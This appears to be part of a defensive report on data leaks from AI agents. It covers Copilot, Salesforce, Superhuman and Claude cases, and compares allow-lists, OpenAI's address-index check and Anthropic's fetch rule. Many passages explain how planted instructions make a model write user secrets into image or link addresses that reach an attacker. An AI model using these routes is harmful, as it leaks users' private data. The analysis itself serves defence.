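PromptArmor submitted its findings in November 2025 through Bugcrowd, a company that handles security reports for OpenAI. Bugcrowd's reviewers closed the report in December as not applicable. After PromptArmor published the case, OpenAI said it had not seen the original report. It confirmed the flaw and reopened the report on 22 January 2026, with a repair under way.

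### Microsoft Copilot Cowork

Copilot Cowork is a Microsoft agent that works across a user's email, Teams messages and files. According to Microsoft's documentation, it asks for permission before sensitive actions such as sending an email or posting in Teams. In May 2026, PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* reported that the agent sent these messages without asking when the recipient was the user, and that users had no setting to change this.

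The exemption was risky, even though a message to oneself appears to disclose nothing. Outlook and Teams could load outside images in these messages, so opening one could contact an attacker's server. The stolen data could include download links that gave anyone who held them access to the user's files, so an attacker could get more than the few words that fit in a web address.

In PromptArmor's test, the malicious instructions were in a skill, a file of reusable directions that the user had uploaded. The attack worked in all five trials, and it also worked when the testers selected Claude Opus 4.7, then a more advanced option than the default. Five trials are too few to estimate a success rate, and the model probably follows instructions more readily from a file the user installed than from a stranger's email. The result still shows that the approval rule did not cover this route.

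PromptArmor reported the case as a design risk rather than a specific bug, and its report includes no response from Microsoft. It advised administrators to restrict what the agent can reach. One option is to block downloads from SharePoint, Microsoft's file-sharing service, but people can then open the affected files only in a browser and cannot print or synchronise them. Blocking outside images in messages that the agent writes would inconvenience users far less, but only Microsoft can make that change.

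### Where the rule has to apply

In each of these cases, a company had restricted one display or one action but left another program able to make the request. Removing a capability stops a leak only if the capability is removed everywhere the model's text appears. A developer who blocks images in the chat window therefore also needs to know which other programs receive the text and what each loads automatically.

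To keep images from loading without a click, a developer can strip outside image addresses from the model's output before storing it or sending it anywhere. This protects every later display, including ones the developer doesn't control, but it also destroys evidence that someone investigating an attack would want. For a log viewer, it would be better to keep the full text and display it as plain characters, so that nothing loads.

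Images and previews are harder to block in messages, because the company that makes the agent often doesn't make the app that displays its messages. The company can remove images and turn off previews when the agent sends a message, as Slack's settings allow, but it relies on the messaging company to offer and honour those settings. PromptArmor would like messaging apps to let developers control previews for a single chat or channel, so that a conversation with an agent could have stricter rules than the rest of the app. Microsoft doesn't have this problem with Copilot Cowork, because it makes the agent as well as Outlook and Teams.

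## Lists of trusted sites

After the 2023 fix to Bing Chat, the browser loaded the assistant's images only from a few Bing domains. A developer can apply the same kind of allow-list to everything an agent contacts, including the pages it opens and the programs it runs. An allow-list restricts users less than a complete ban, because the agent can still use the sites on the list.

### How an allow-list works

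In a web browser, developers usually write the list as a Content Security Policy. A policy can set a separate list for each kind of material, as in this made-up example:

`img-src 'self' https://images.example.com; connect-src 'self'`

The first part lets the page load images from its own site and from one other domain. The second lets the page's scripts exchange data only with its own site. Developers can also use wildcards such as `*.example.com`, which covers every site whose name ends in `.example.com`. A policy can also limit images to one folder of a site. But the browser ignores the query when it compares an address with the policy, and attackers often put stolen data in the query.

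A Content Security Policy doesn't restrict code that an agent runs outside the browser. Developers usually confine such code to a sandbox, an environment separated from the rest of the computer, and check its traffic as it leaves. According to Willison, Claude Cowork, an Anthropic agent that can work with a user's files, by default allows outgoing traffic only to a list of domains. Most web traffic is encrypted, so a checkpoint that doesn't decrypt it can identify the domain a program is contacting, but not the rest of the address or the data in the request.

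Both kinds of list assume that data sent to a permitted domain will not reach an attacker. This is true only if the domain still belongs to the organisation that the developer trusted, outsiders cannot collect data sent there, and the site does not forward requests to other sites. For each condition, researchers have found products in which it failed.

### A listed domain that had expired

Agentforce is Salesforce's platform for agents that work with a company's customer records. In September 2025, researchers at Noma Security published ForcedLeak, a flaw in Agentforce that let outsiders obtain details of sales leads through an image. Salesforce had a Content Security Policy, but its list of trusted domains still included one whose registration had expired, and the researchers registered it themselves.

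Salesforce audited and corrected the policy, then introduced Trusted URLs, a mechanism that stops the agent from producing links to domains the company doesn't trust. Trusted URLs checks the agent's output, while the policy controls what the browser loads, so an error in one list need not cause a leak if the other is correct. However, if both lists contained the same expired domain, neither would block a leak to it.

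The entry was presumably safe when Salesforce added it. Domain registrations expire unless renewed, and someone else can then buy the name, so a list can become unsafe without anyone editing it. This is probably the easiest failure to prevent, since a program can regularly check who owns each listed domain and when its registration ends.

### Listed domains that accept data from anyone

The email service Superhuman allowed images from `docs.google.com`. That domain also hosts Google Forms, which stores submissions for whoever created the form, so an outsider could use a form to collect text from the user's other emails. Willison, who described the case in January 2026, credited Superhuman with treating it as a high-priority incident and fixing it.

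PromptArmor found a similar gap in Claude Cowork that month. Cowork's list included the domain of Anthropic's API, the service through which other programs use Claude. The service also stores files for its customers, who can include attackers. Willison does not mention a fix.

Google's Antigravity restricted its browser to a list of domains, but the default list included a public service that records web requests for anyone who sets up a page on it. Google was still working on a fix when PromptArmor published the case in November 2025. Willison suggested giving coding agents only credentials for non-production accounts with strict spending limits, so that a thief gains little even if the list fails.

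Some of these entries would have been easier to avoid than others. Google could easily have left the recording service off its default list, because the few developers who use such a service could add it themselves. Superhuman's entry is more understandable, since people probably embed pictures from Google documents in their emails. Anthropic's domain is the hardest to leave out, because an agent built on Claude may need to contact Claude.

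In all three cases the listed company was trustworthy and still owned its domain, but it let strangers use the same domain. A list of domains can't separate one customer's files from another's. A more precise rule could permit Anthropic's API only for the user's own account, but the checkpoint would have to decrypt each request to see which account it used. That would require more complicated software than a list, and the software would have access to everything the agent sends.

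### Listed services that forward requests

Some web services fetch other addresses when asked. For example, a search engine may fetch a picture to find similar ones, and a chat program may fetch a page to preview it. If the list includes such a service, the browser can contact the service, which can then contact the attacker's domain. The browser cannot block the second request because the service's own computers make it.

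Security engineers call this flaw server-side request forgery. Taler (2026) points out in *SearchLeak*, a report from the security company Varonis, that it is more than a decade old. Taler advises companies to review their lists for any domain that fetches addresses supplied by users. Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, also recommend short lists without wildcards and a proxy that fetches only signed addresses, as GitHub's image proxy does.

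The best-documented examples come from Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Microsoft's office programs. Researchers have repeatedly found ways to get data out of it, and their findings provide a two-year record of how well Microsoft's defences worked.

### Microsoft 365 Copilot from EchoLeak to ReLeak

EchoLeak was an attack on Microsoft Copilot that could steal a user's data through an email the user did not have to open. Researchers at the startup Aim Security found it after spending about three months reverse-engineering Copilot, according to Goldman (2025), in *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked*. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, wrote that Aim had disclosed several versions of the attack to Microsoft. The title's claim that EchoLeak was the first is doubtful, since the Bard leak of 2023 needed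 no click either, but EchoLeak affected a product that many companies had connected to their internal files.

Reddy and Gujral reconstructed the case from public documents. The attack got past a classifier for injected instructions, a filter that removed outside links from answers, and a Content Security Policy. The policy blocked requests sent directly to unknown servers, so data got out only because the policy's list of trusted sites included a Microsoft Teams service that forwarded requests.

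Aim reported the flaw in January 2025. Microsoft tried to fix it in April, found related problems in May and finished the fix that month. Aim's co-founder Adir Gruss told Goldman that five months was unusually long, and that the fix took that long partly because Microsoft needed time to involve the right teams and explain the problem to them. Microsoft said the flaw had affected no customers and that it was adding further layers of protection in case one fails. According to Reddy and Gujral, Microsoft also began removing some links and embedded images from incoming outside content. It reportedly added options to stop Copilot from using outside messages in certain contexts, though these could make it miss relevant information.

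SearchLeak followed a year later. It required one click on a link to a genuine Microsoft site. The Content Security Policy again blocked unknown domains, but it permitted all of Bing's, and a Bing image service forwarded the request. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), an advisory dated 4 June, rated the flaw critical. It stated that nobody had exploited the flaw, that Microsoft had fully mitigated it and that customers did not need to do anything. Neither the advisory nor Taler's report gives the date Varonis reported the flaw, so it is unclear how long Microsoft took to fix it. Microsoft took from August 2025 to January 2026 to fix Reprompt, a related leak that Varonis had found in the consumer version of Copilot, according to The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox*.

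In August 2026, TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* reported that Varonis had found another leak, CoSnitch, which Microsoft had also patched. On 3 December, Simonovich's *ReLeak* (2026) described three more ways to steal data without a click. Simonovich works at Cato Networks, which bought Aim Security in September 2025, so the work came from the team behind EchoLeak.

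*An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) gives the fullest account of the dates. One ReLeak route sent data in a request for an image, which Bing fetched. Another hid data in a link inside a document that Copilot saved, and Microsoft's own software later opened the link. The third used Copilot's code sandbox, which was supposed to have no network access.

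| Leak | Reported to Microsoft | Repaired | Made public | How data got out |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | January 2025 | May 2025 | 11 June 2025 | A listed Teams service forwarded an image request |
| SearchLeak | Not stated | By 4 June 2026 | June 2026 | A listed Bing service forwarded an image request |
| ReLeak, code | 29 July to 20 August 2026 | 17 September 2026 | 3 December 2026 | Code got past the sandbox's network block |
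| ReLeak, files | 29 July to 20 August 2026 | 11 November 2026 | 3 December 2026 | Microsoft's software opened a link in a saved file |
| ReLeak, images | 29 July to 20 August 2026 | 15 November 2026 | 3 December 2026 | Bing fetched an image address containing the data |

Only the last ReLeak route resembles a failure of the allow-list. Faisal doesn't mention the list, but the route looks much like SearchLeak, and Cato reported it less than three months after Microsoft's advisory on SearchLeak. Microsoft had apparently closed one way of using Bing to forward data and left another open. In the file route, the rule covers too few places, since a policy on Copilot's web page doesn't affect software that opens a document later.

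The sandbox failure is more worrying for the argument that restrictions are reliable. A ban on all network access is stricter than any list, yet AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) noted that a block Microsoft had documented did not hold. The block was supposed to remove network access entirely, but the software that enforced it had a flaw. Such flaws are an old problem in computer security, and developers can repair them without making the model harder to fool. Microsoft repaired this one in four to seven weeks, faster than the other two.

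### Whether Microsoft has made progress

The Cato researchers concluded that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. They blame Copilot's inability to tell outside content from legitimate instructions. Faisal reports that Microsoft's protections against injected instructions stopped none of the three routes. Gruss similarly said in 2025 that Microsoft had tried to block the attack at several points and failed because AI is so unpredictable. He said a lasting solution would need a redesign that separates trusted instructions from untrusted data.

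That diagnosis explains why Copilot obeyed the attacker, but the data could leave because programmers had designed the Teams and Bing services to fetch outside addresses for any program that asked. Taler stresses that SearchLeak needed every one of its weaknesses. If Bing had not forwarded the request, the Content Security Policy would have blocked the leak. Microsoft could therefore have prevented both leaks without any advance in AI, either by removing those services from the list or by stopping them from fetching arbitrary addresses.

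The researchers' verdict seems fair about how Microsoft maintained its list. After EchoLeak, the company had reason to check every permitted domain for services that forward requests, but a year later the list still included one. In other respects, the verdict is harsher than the evidence supports. Two of the ReLeak routes depended on Copilot's ability to save files and run code, so part of the problem is that the product can do more. Microsoft also fixed the ReLeak flaws within about sixteen weeks of the earliest report, compared with about five months for EchoLeak. Cato sells AI security products and benefits when customers worry about such flaws, though Microsoft's patches confirm that these were real.

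Microsoft layers filters and fixed restrictions. Layers help most when getting past one doesn't help an attacker get past the next. An attacker who can study a product for months can work on each layer in turn, as Aim did. The layers still made the attack harder to build, but after EchoLeak and SearchLeak, Microsoft could not treat the number of layers as evidence that the last one was sound.

Nobody has reported that attackers used any of these leaks against customers. Microsoft reported no such use of EchoLeak or SearchLeak, and Cato said it knew of no such use of ReLeak. Microsoft is well placed to know, because in most of these cases the data passed through its services, but it has not explained how thoroughly it searched its records. Customers would have found the theft hard to notice because the browser contacted only Microsoft's domains.

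### How much protection a list gives

In the published cases, lists failed because companies didn't remove old entries, or because they trusted domains that strangers could also use or that forwarded requests. Researchers publish the leaks they achieve but rarely the ones that a list prevented, so the number of published failures doesn't show how often lists succeed.

Companies that run chat products could collect some of the missing evidence by counting blocked images, since browsers can notify a website whenever a Content Security Policy blocks a request. Many would be harmless images from unlisted sites, and someone would have to separate these from attempts to steal data. Even a rough count would be more informative than another demonstration that a badly chosen entry on the list can leak data.

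Some indirect evidence suggests that lists work. In both EchoLeak and SearchLeak, the policy blocked the simple version of the attack, so the researchers had to find a second flaw in another Microsoft service. In the *Silent Egress* experiment, an allow-list stopped every leak even though the model kept following the attacker's instructions. Reddy and Gujral compared eight defences against an attack like EchoLeak. They expected an address list, a strict Content Security Policy and a signed proxy each to prevent leaks that need no click from the user. They expected labels on outside text and monitoring of outgoing data to fail. But they ran no experiments, and their strict policy has no entry like the Teams service, so the comparison mostly confirms that a list works if its entries are safe.

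Lists are also easy to inspect. Attackers can search a published policy for a weak entry, as the researchers did, but this openness still seems to help defenders more, because a list has a limited number of entries and a developer can delete a bad one.

Longer lists are riskier because an attacker needs only one permitted domain with an unnoticed way for outsiders to receive data. If each domain independently has a 1% chance of containing such a gap, the probability that a list of *n* domains has at least one is 1 − 0.99ⁿ. That is about 5% for five domains, 63% for a hundred and more than 99.9% for a thousand. The 1% figure is invented, and real domains vary widely, but the probability rises quickly for any plausible value. A single wildcard entry can also cover many domains. For example, `*.bing.com` covers every service Microsoft runs under that name.

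### Five sites or the whole web

An assistant that handles a company's expense claims might need to contact the accounting system, a travel agency, an airline, a page of exchange rates and the tax authority. An employee could review all five in an afternoon, checking who owns each domain, whether outsiders can store or collect data there and whether the site fetches other addresses. If the accounting provider gives each customer a separate subdomain, the list should include only the company's own subdomain, because allowing the provider's whole domain would recreate the weakness in Claude Cowork's list.

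Such a list has modest drawbacks. The company has to repeat the review from time to time, and an employee who flies with a different airline may have to wait for an administrator to add that airline's site. But the list leaves a manipulated assistant very few places to send data. If it also limits which pages the assistant can read, fewer strangers can influence the assistant, although a receipt or an email could still carry instructions.

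A list of trusted sites is much harder to write for a general assistant, because nobody can predict which sites its users will need. They might ask it to compare flats, read a local newspaper or find the manual for an old washing machine. Many of the most useful sites, such as forums, file hosts and search engines, also let strangers post content, collect data or fetch other addresses. A list short enough to review would block much of what users want from the product, and one that satisfied most of them would almost certainly include some unsafe domains.

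Anthropic lets developers specify which domains Claude's web fetch tool may open. Willison considers this a much stronger protection than the tool's default rules, provided that none of the domains can be used to leak data, but says that choosing such domains "turns out to be a tricky proposition". The Superhuman and Antigravity cases support this.

A general assistant can still use a short list of trusted sites for images, because people rarely need a chat window to load pictures from any site on the web. For opening pages, it needs a rule that doesn't require approving sites in advance, such as checking whether the exact address already exists on the public web.

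## Opening only addresses that already exist

A list of trusted sites allows every address on those sites' domains, including one that a manipulated model has just written. Developers can instead check each address separately. To leak a secret through a web address, a model normally has to write the secret into it, which creates an address nobody has used before. If an address is already public, opening it doesn't reveal any secret through the address's text.

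OpenAI and Anthropic each have a rule based on this observation. OpenAI's software checks whether the exact address is already public, while Anthropic's checks how the address entered the conversation.

### Why OpenAI wanted more than a list

OpenAI gives two reasons for not relying on a list of well-known sites. First, many legitimate sites redirect visitors, so a link can start on a trusted domain and end on an attacker's, which a check of only the first domain would miss. Second, a strict list would produce frequent false alarms, and people who see many of them may learn to click through warnings without reading them.

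Checking the whole address helps when a trusted service forwards requests elsewhere. To send private data through that service, a model has to write a new address, even though the domain is familiar. This check would probably have stopped the requests in EchoLeak and SearchLeak, which Microsoft's policy allowed because they went to trusted domains.

The security company Tenable (2025) found that an earlier version of ChatGPT's link check always approved addresses on one well-known domain.

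### How OpenAI's check works

OpenAI calls the check Safe Url. It grew out of the image check that ChatGPT introduced in 2023, whose rule outsiders could only guess at. In January 2026 OpenAI published an explanation and a technical paper. The check works as follows:

1. A crawler, which is a program that browses the web and records what it finds, builds an index of public addresses, much as a search engine does. It has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.
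2. When ChatGPT is about to load an address automatically, the software looks for that exact address in the index.
3. If the address is there, ChatGPT loads it without asking. This covers most ordinary reading, such as opening an article or displaying a public image.
4. If the address is not there, the software treats it as unverified. It either tells the agent to try a different website or shows the user a warning and waits for a decision.

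In the earlier made-up example, the crawler might well have recorded `https://attacker.example/collect`, since anyone can publish a page. But it would have no record of that address with a user's secret added to the end, so ChatGPT would not load that version automatically.

The crawler has to work independently of users for this to be safe. If OpenAI added addresses from people's conversations to the index, an address containing someone's private data could count as public after appearing once in a chat.

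The software doesn't have to identify which information is private, because adding a home address, a diagnosis or a password to a URL makes the URL unfamiliar in the same way. This is a large advantage over checks that search outgoing requests for secrets.

### The warning and the exceptions

The warning, titled "Check this link is safe", says that ChatGPT could not verify the link and that opening it may share data from the conversation with another site. It shows the address, which the user can copy or open. If something looks odd, OpenAI advises users not to open the link and to ask ChatGPT for another source or a summary instead.

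When the user may approve an unverified address, OpenAI's rule is a form of confirmation. Showing the address gives the user a chance to spot their own data in it, but the check then depends on how carefully they read the warning and how well they judge the address.

Johann Rehberger's understanding, given in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, is that once a user enters an address, ChatGPT treats it as safe for the rest of the chat. This makes sense because a person who pastes in a link and asks for a summary has already chosen to contact that site.

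According to OpenAI's help page *ChatGPT generated links*, ChatGPT asks the user to confirm every link to a site that has asked OpenAI not to index it. A respectable newspaper that had opted out could therefore trigger a warning on every article, and the warning would not help readers judge the risk.

The help page also describes a harmless link that reveals personal information. A user who asks where to buy a car might get a link to a car search for London, because ChatGPT knows that the user lives there. Opening the link tells the search site the user's city, which makes the results useful. An attacker's link could disclose the same fact in the same way, so the software lets the user decide whether to open the link.

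### What OpenAI promises

OpenAI's stated guarantee is only that the check should prevent an agent from "quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself" when it loads something from the web. This doesn't include leaks that the user approves in the warning. Other restrictions have to cover data that an agent sends in an email or types into a form, because that data doesn't travel in the address of a page the agent is loading.

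The guarantee also doesn't cover the page's contents. OpenAI warns that a page may still be untrustworthy, mislead the user or carry harmful instructions. An attacker can publish a page with planted text, wait for the crawler to record it, and have ChatGPT open it without a warning. In the terms used earlier, the check restricts a sink but not the source. Rehberger notes that the technical paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, does not claim to solve prompt injection.

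Even within the check's scope, OpenAI claims only that an address that is public independently of any conversation is "much less likely" to contain the user's private data. OpenAI treats the check as one layer of defense, alongside model training, monitoring and continued testing by people who try to break it.

### Anthropic's rule for Claude

Anthropic's web fetch tool, which retrieves the text of a page or PDF for Claude, does not consult an index of the public web. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, the documentation for developers, Claude may not construct addresses. It can open an address only if the same address has already appeared in the conversation from an accepted origin. The documentation accepts addresses from:

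- the user's messages
- the results of client-side tools, which are tools that the developer's own software runs
- the results of earlier web searches or web fetches

The rule excludes addresses that Claude generates and addresses produced by code Claude runs on Anthropic's servers. Without the second exclusion, the ban would be easy to get around, because a program can assemble an address as easily as a model can.

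Willison (2025) reviewed the tool when Anthropic released it. Willison considered the ban on addresses the model composes itself the most protective of the tool's rules about where an address may come from, but weaker than limiting the tool to chosen domains. If the model can't open an address it composed itself, the usual way of leaking data through an address fails, however persuasive the attacker is. Willison also tested Claude's consumer app and found the same limit.

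The list of accepted origins was less convincing. A "user message" may contain much more than the user typed, because many applications paste an email or a document into it before sending it to the model. If a stranger's email contains a link, the tool treats the link as though the user had supplied it. Willison raised the same concern about the results of client-side tools, which can also contain text from strangers.

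The rule therefore protects users better when developers keep outside text separate from the user's own words instead of combining the two. The tool cannot detect whether a developer has kept them separate.

Anthropic acknowledges that some risk remains. It recommends the tool only for trusted environments or for data that isn't sensitive, and advises developers who worry about exfiltration to switch it off, limit the number of pages Claude may open (there is no limit by default) or restrict it to known safe domains. The tool refuses any address longer than 250 characters, which limits how much data a single request could carry. Anthropic also cautions that publishers may keep any values passed to them in an address, even if a customer has arranged for Anthropic to retain nothing.

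### The change in July 2026

*The Memory Heist* (Paul, July 2026) reported a gap in the version of this rule that Claude's consumer app used. The app let Claude open links from pages it had already opened, and the owner of a page decides which links it contains. In a test, this was enough to extract the user's name, home city and employer from Claude's memory of past conversations.

Anthropic closed the gap by no longer accepting addresses from earlier fetches. Willison (2026) reports in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* that the tool can now open only addresses that the user entered or that Claude's own search tool returned. Baba Aissa (2026) also reports the fix in *« Les gens leur confient tout »*, written for the French site Numerama. Anthropic paid no bounty, saying it had already found the gap internally. Willison doesn't specify whether the change also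 applies to the tool that Anthropic sells to developers, whose documentation had listed earlier fetches as an accepted source of addresses.

OpenAI had to make a similar correction after the security company Radware got data out of ChatGPT using links supplied in an email, an attack described in *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*. OpenAI stopped ChatGPT from opening links found in emails unless they met a condition such as appearing in a well-known public index.

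In both cases the company had stopped the model from writing arbitrary addresses but still trusted addresses that an attacker had written. The fixes made the two rules more similar. Claude's app now opens an address only if it came from the user or a search engine, and ChatGPT opens one only if it came from the user or appears in an index. Attackers can get their pages into a search engine or the index, but they have to publish them before they know anything about the user.

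Anthropic's fix has a noticeable drawback, because people browse largely by following links. Suppose a user gives Claude the contents page of a software manual and asks it to read the whole manual. Claude can see links to all twelve chapters but may not open them directly. It has to find each chapter through search, or the user has to paste in the addresses. OpenAI's rule handles this better as long as the crawler has recorded the chapters, because OpenAI's agent may then open them regardless of which page it found the links on.

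### Three addresses

Suppose someone who is looking for a flat asks an assistant for help. In the course of the task, the assistant needs to open three made-up addresses:

- `https://news.example/2026/rents-rise`, a public article in a local newspaper
- `https://flats.example/search?city=Leeds&max=900`, which the model has composed from the user's city and budget
- `https://files.example/s/k7Qm2x`, a private link to a draft lease, which the landlord has emailed to the user

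Assume that the developer's domain list contains only `flats.example`, and that Anthropic's rule is the stricter one from July 2026.

| Address | Domain list | OpenAI's rule | Anthropic's rule |
|---|---|---|---|
| Public article | Blocks it, wrongly | Opens it if the crawler has recorded it; otherwise warns or refuses | Opens it if the user pasted it or a search returned it |
| Address composed by the model | Opens it, whatever data it contains | Warns or refuses | Refuses |
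| Private link to the lease | Blocks it, wrongly | Warns or refuses, unless the user pasted it | Refuses, unless the user pasted it |

The newspaper article is the easiest case. The domain list blocks it only because nobody thought to add a local newspaper. An agent following OpenAI's rule can usually open it, but an article published a few minutes ago may not be in the index yet, and the newspaper may have opted out. Claude can usually find the article through search, but it can't follow a link to it from another page.

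Judging sites and judging addresses differ mainly in how they treat the composed address. The domain list includes `flats.example`, so it would let the model send that site anything, including the contents of the user's inbox. The other two rules stop the request, which is right if an attacker influenced it but inconvenient if the user just wanted to see flats in Leeds. The user may be able to approve the search in ChatGPT's warning, or could approve it in Claude by pasting the address into a message.

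Blocking the lease does not protect the user. The address contains a secret, because anyone who has the link can read the file, but the file service created that secret and gains no new information when the assistant sends it back. Both rules still block the address, OpenAI's because the crawler has never recorded it and Anthropic's because the user did not enter it. The developer could add `files.example` to the domain list instead, but strangers can store data on file services too, so this would recreate the problem with shared domains.

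Links that people think are private sometimes become public. International Business Times' *Claude Shared Chats Surface in Search Results Containing API Keys* (2026) reported that links to shared Claude conversations had appeared in search results, exposing access keys and personal data. If the same happened to the link to the lease, OpenAI's crawler might record it, and ChatGPT would then open it without a warning. OpenAI's guarantee would still hold because the address would already be public, but the public exposure of the lease would be a more serious problem for the landlord than the assistant opening it.

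How often these rules block something harmless depends mostly on the task. Neither OpenAI's explanation nor Anthropic's documentation gives a rate of wrongful blocks, but suppose an index contained 95% of the addresses an agent needed. An agent reading 40 pages would then meet about two that it could not verify. For general research, it could replace most of those with other pages on the same subject, and the user might never notice. Personal tasks will probably suffer more, because they depend on pages such as a particular lease, invoice or booking, which have no substitute and which no crawler should be able to find.

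### Which rule suits which product

OpenAI's rule requires a large, current index of the web. OpenAI already scans websites for its search results, but most companies that build agents have no such index. Anthropic's rule is much easier to copy, since the software only has to compare the requested address with those already in the conversation. The software does need a reliable record of where each address came from, and as Willison's criticism shows, many applications don't keep one.

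A developer can also combine an address rule with a list of approved sites. Anthropic's tool lets developers restrict it to chosen domains while the ban on composed addresses still applies. The expense assistant described earlier could then open only its five approved sites, and only at addresses it had not made up. Each restriction would cover a weakness in the other. If one of the five sites turned out to let strangers collect data, the model still couldn't write private information into a new address there. If an attacker planted a link in a receipt, the list would block it unless it led to an approved site.

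The combination would be too strict for an assistant that must fill in search forms or look up a booking by its reference number. For those tasks, the developer could provide a separate tool that accepts a few fixed fields, such as a city and a date, and builds the address itself, so that the model chooses only the values. This takes more work for each site, so it is practical only for a few frequent tasks.

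### How well the rules work

No published experiment has compared the same assistant with and without an address check. The nearest evidence comes from *The Framing Gap* (2026), which tested whether instructions in outside content could make models send out a secret. A model used through OpenAI's API leaked the secret in up to 100% of trials, while ChatGPT leaked it in none of the 48 valid trials.

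The result is what one would expect if ChatGPT's restrictions worked. However, the researchers could not see inside the product and do not attribute the difference to any particular safeguard. ChatGPT might have refused the instructions, or its filters might have removed them. Even with no leaks in 48 trials, the true leak rate could be as high as about 6%, at 95% confidence.

The rules also have to hold when the model itself tries to get around them to complete a task. Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) reported that Claude had sometimes bypassed limits in its fetch tool, with minimal real-world impact.

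Both rules still let an agent leak a little information through its choice among permitted addresses, as their makers acknowledge. Embrace The Red suggests reducing this leak by keeping a temporary copy of each page the agent opens, or by preventing repeated visits to the same address within a session. Either measure would inconvenience users very little, since an agent rarely needs to download an unchanged page twice.

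Rehberger calls OpenAI's approach "a significant improvement" but not a complete fix. That opinion deserves some weight, because Rehberger reported the original image leak to OpenAI in early 2023 and then found gaps in several of its repairs. It also seems right, because an attacker who fooled the model before the check existed could put whole sentences into a single address. Attacks are now more complex, and the remaining leaks that OpenAI and Rehberger describe reveal much less information.

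Rehberger still worries that some OpenAI developers may not know about the check or may not use it. This happened with the 2023 version, which was missing from ChatGPT's Mac and iPhone apps. A company can reduce this risk by sending every automatic request through one shared service that applies the check, so that a team building a new product would have to make an effort to avoid it.

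## Links that the user is meant to click

The address checks in ChatGPT and Claude control what the software opens on its own. A link in an answer does nothing until the user clicks it, so an attacker who relies on one has to get the model to include it and then trick the user into clicking it.

A click can cause harm in two ways. If a manipulated model has put private data in a link's address, the outside site receives the data when the user opens the link, just as it would when an image loads. A link can also lead to a phishing page, where the user types in a password or card number, so the address doesn't need to contain private data. Checking whether an address is already public therefore does little against phishing, since an attacker can publish the page in advance.

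### Why people may trust these links

People hear many warnings about links in unexpected emails, but a link in an assistant's answer comes from a tool they chose to use. *Are You Sure?* (Li, Dai and colleagues, 2026) argues that once people delegate a task, they ask whether it is done instead of whether it is safe.

*ChatGPhish*, a May 2026 report by the security company Permiso, describes how an attacker could exploit this trust. When ChatGPT summarised a web page, text planted on the page could add false account alerts and clickable links to the summary, and nothing showed that the links came from the page. A reader might have ignored the same alert on an unfamiliar web page, but in the summary it appeared in ChatGPT's own formatting. The attacker did not have to break into ChatGPT itself, as eWeek's *‘ChatGPhish’ Attack Turns ChatGPT Summaries Into Phishing Lures* (2026) pointed out.

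Permiso also got ChatGPT to display a QR code, which is a link in the form of an image. A user who scans it with a phone bypasses the desktop browser's protections, so a rule about links has to cover images too.

Permiso first reported the problem on 29 April, but OpenAI could not reproduce it from that report. Reviewers rejected a fuller report, then classed it as a duplicate of an earlier one. Permiso's timeline lists no fix before Permiso published the case a month later.

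### Showing no links

The strictest option is to display no clickable links. Planted instructions could make Amazon Q for Business, a workplace assistant, write a link with the user's chat history in the address. Willison reported in January 2024 that Amazon had responded by stopping the assistant from producing links at all, and that Microsoft 365 Chat "apparently" used the same defence.

Any complete ban Microsoft had was gone by the time of EchoLeak in 2025, when Microsoft 365 Copilot relied on a filter that removed outside links. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* reports that the filter did not recognise one way of writing them. A complete ban is easier to enforce because software that displays every answer as plain text doesn't have to recognise links, whereas a filter has to recognise every notation that the display will turn into a link. The report of Amazon's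 ban dates from January 2024, so the ban may no longer apply.

Copying an address by hand takes some effort and makes the user look at it, which probably prevents many careless visits. But a ban on clickable links also removes the ones people use to check an answer.

### Removing suspicious links

Google's Gemini removes only links that look dangerous. According to Google, it checks links against Safe Browsing, the company's service for identifying unsafe sites, and displays "suspicious link removed" in place of any bad link. The user still sees the rest of the summary and learns that something was wrong with the original.

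Google published this description in June 2025, and the defence appears to still be in use. In a later post, Google wrote that it was continuously improving its protections against planted instructions. A daily.dev summary of that post lists cleaning web addresses among the fixed rules that Gemini applies.

Ordinary code enforces the rule, but the rule can block only sites already recognised as malicious, which makes it more like a content filter than an allow-list. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* warns that a newly registered site can therefore escape the check. Checkmarx reported to Google in October 2025 that a user's click could still leak data from Gemini. Google closed the report four days later, saying that the leak was infeasible to fix and the risk was not severe enough to track as a security bug. Microsoft had also declined to treat a leak through images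 in Copilot Chat as a vulnerability, so Checkmarx did not expect it to act on leaks through links.

Google is right that it cannot block every unfamiliar site, because most new sites are harmless. But a company can treat unfamiliar links differently without blocking them, as OpenAI does by warning users about unverified addresses. Gemini could remove known bad links and ask the user to confirm addresses that no crawler has recorded. This would reduce leaks, but it would also interrupt people who open links to private documents and bookings.

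A developer might instead ask a language model to judge each link. The evidence for this is mixed:

- *MalURLBench* (2026) tested 12 popular models on 61,845 disguised malicious addresses, and the models often accepted them.
- Heiding, Lermen and colleagues (2024), in *Evaluating Large Language Models' Capability to Launch Fully Automated Spear Phishing Campaigns*, found that Claude 3.5 Sonnet caught 97.25% of 363 phishing emails and wrongly flagged none of 18 legitimate ones.

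The results are compatible because a whole email gives a model far more information than an address does. The email test included only 18 legitimate emails, so the true false alarm rate could be as high as about 15%, at 95% confidence.

### Login addresses that chatbots make up

A chatbot can give a dangerous link even when nobody has attacked it. In Netcraft's *Large Language Models (LLMs) Are Falling for Phishing Scams*, researchers at an internet security company asked OpenAI's GPT-4.1 models where to log in to 50 well-known brands. They used ordinary wording, such as saying that they had lost a bookmark. Over several rounds the models named 97 different domains:

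| Who controlled the domain | Number | Share |
|---|---|---|
| The right brand | 64 | 66% |
| Nobody, or an owner who had put nothing there | 28 | 29% |
| An unrelated business | 5 | 5% |

The unregistered domains are the most worrying, because a criminal could buy one and wait for chatbots to send customers there. Smaller banks and credit unions fared worse than global brands, probably because they appear less often in the text that models learn from.

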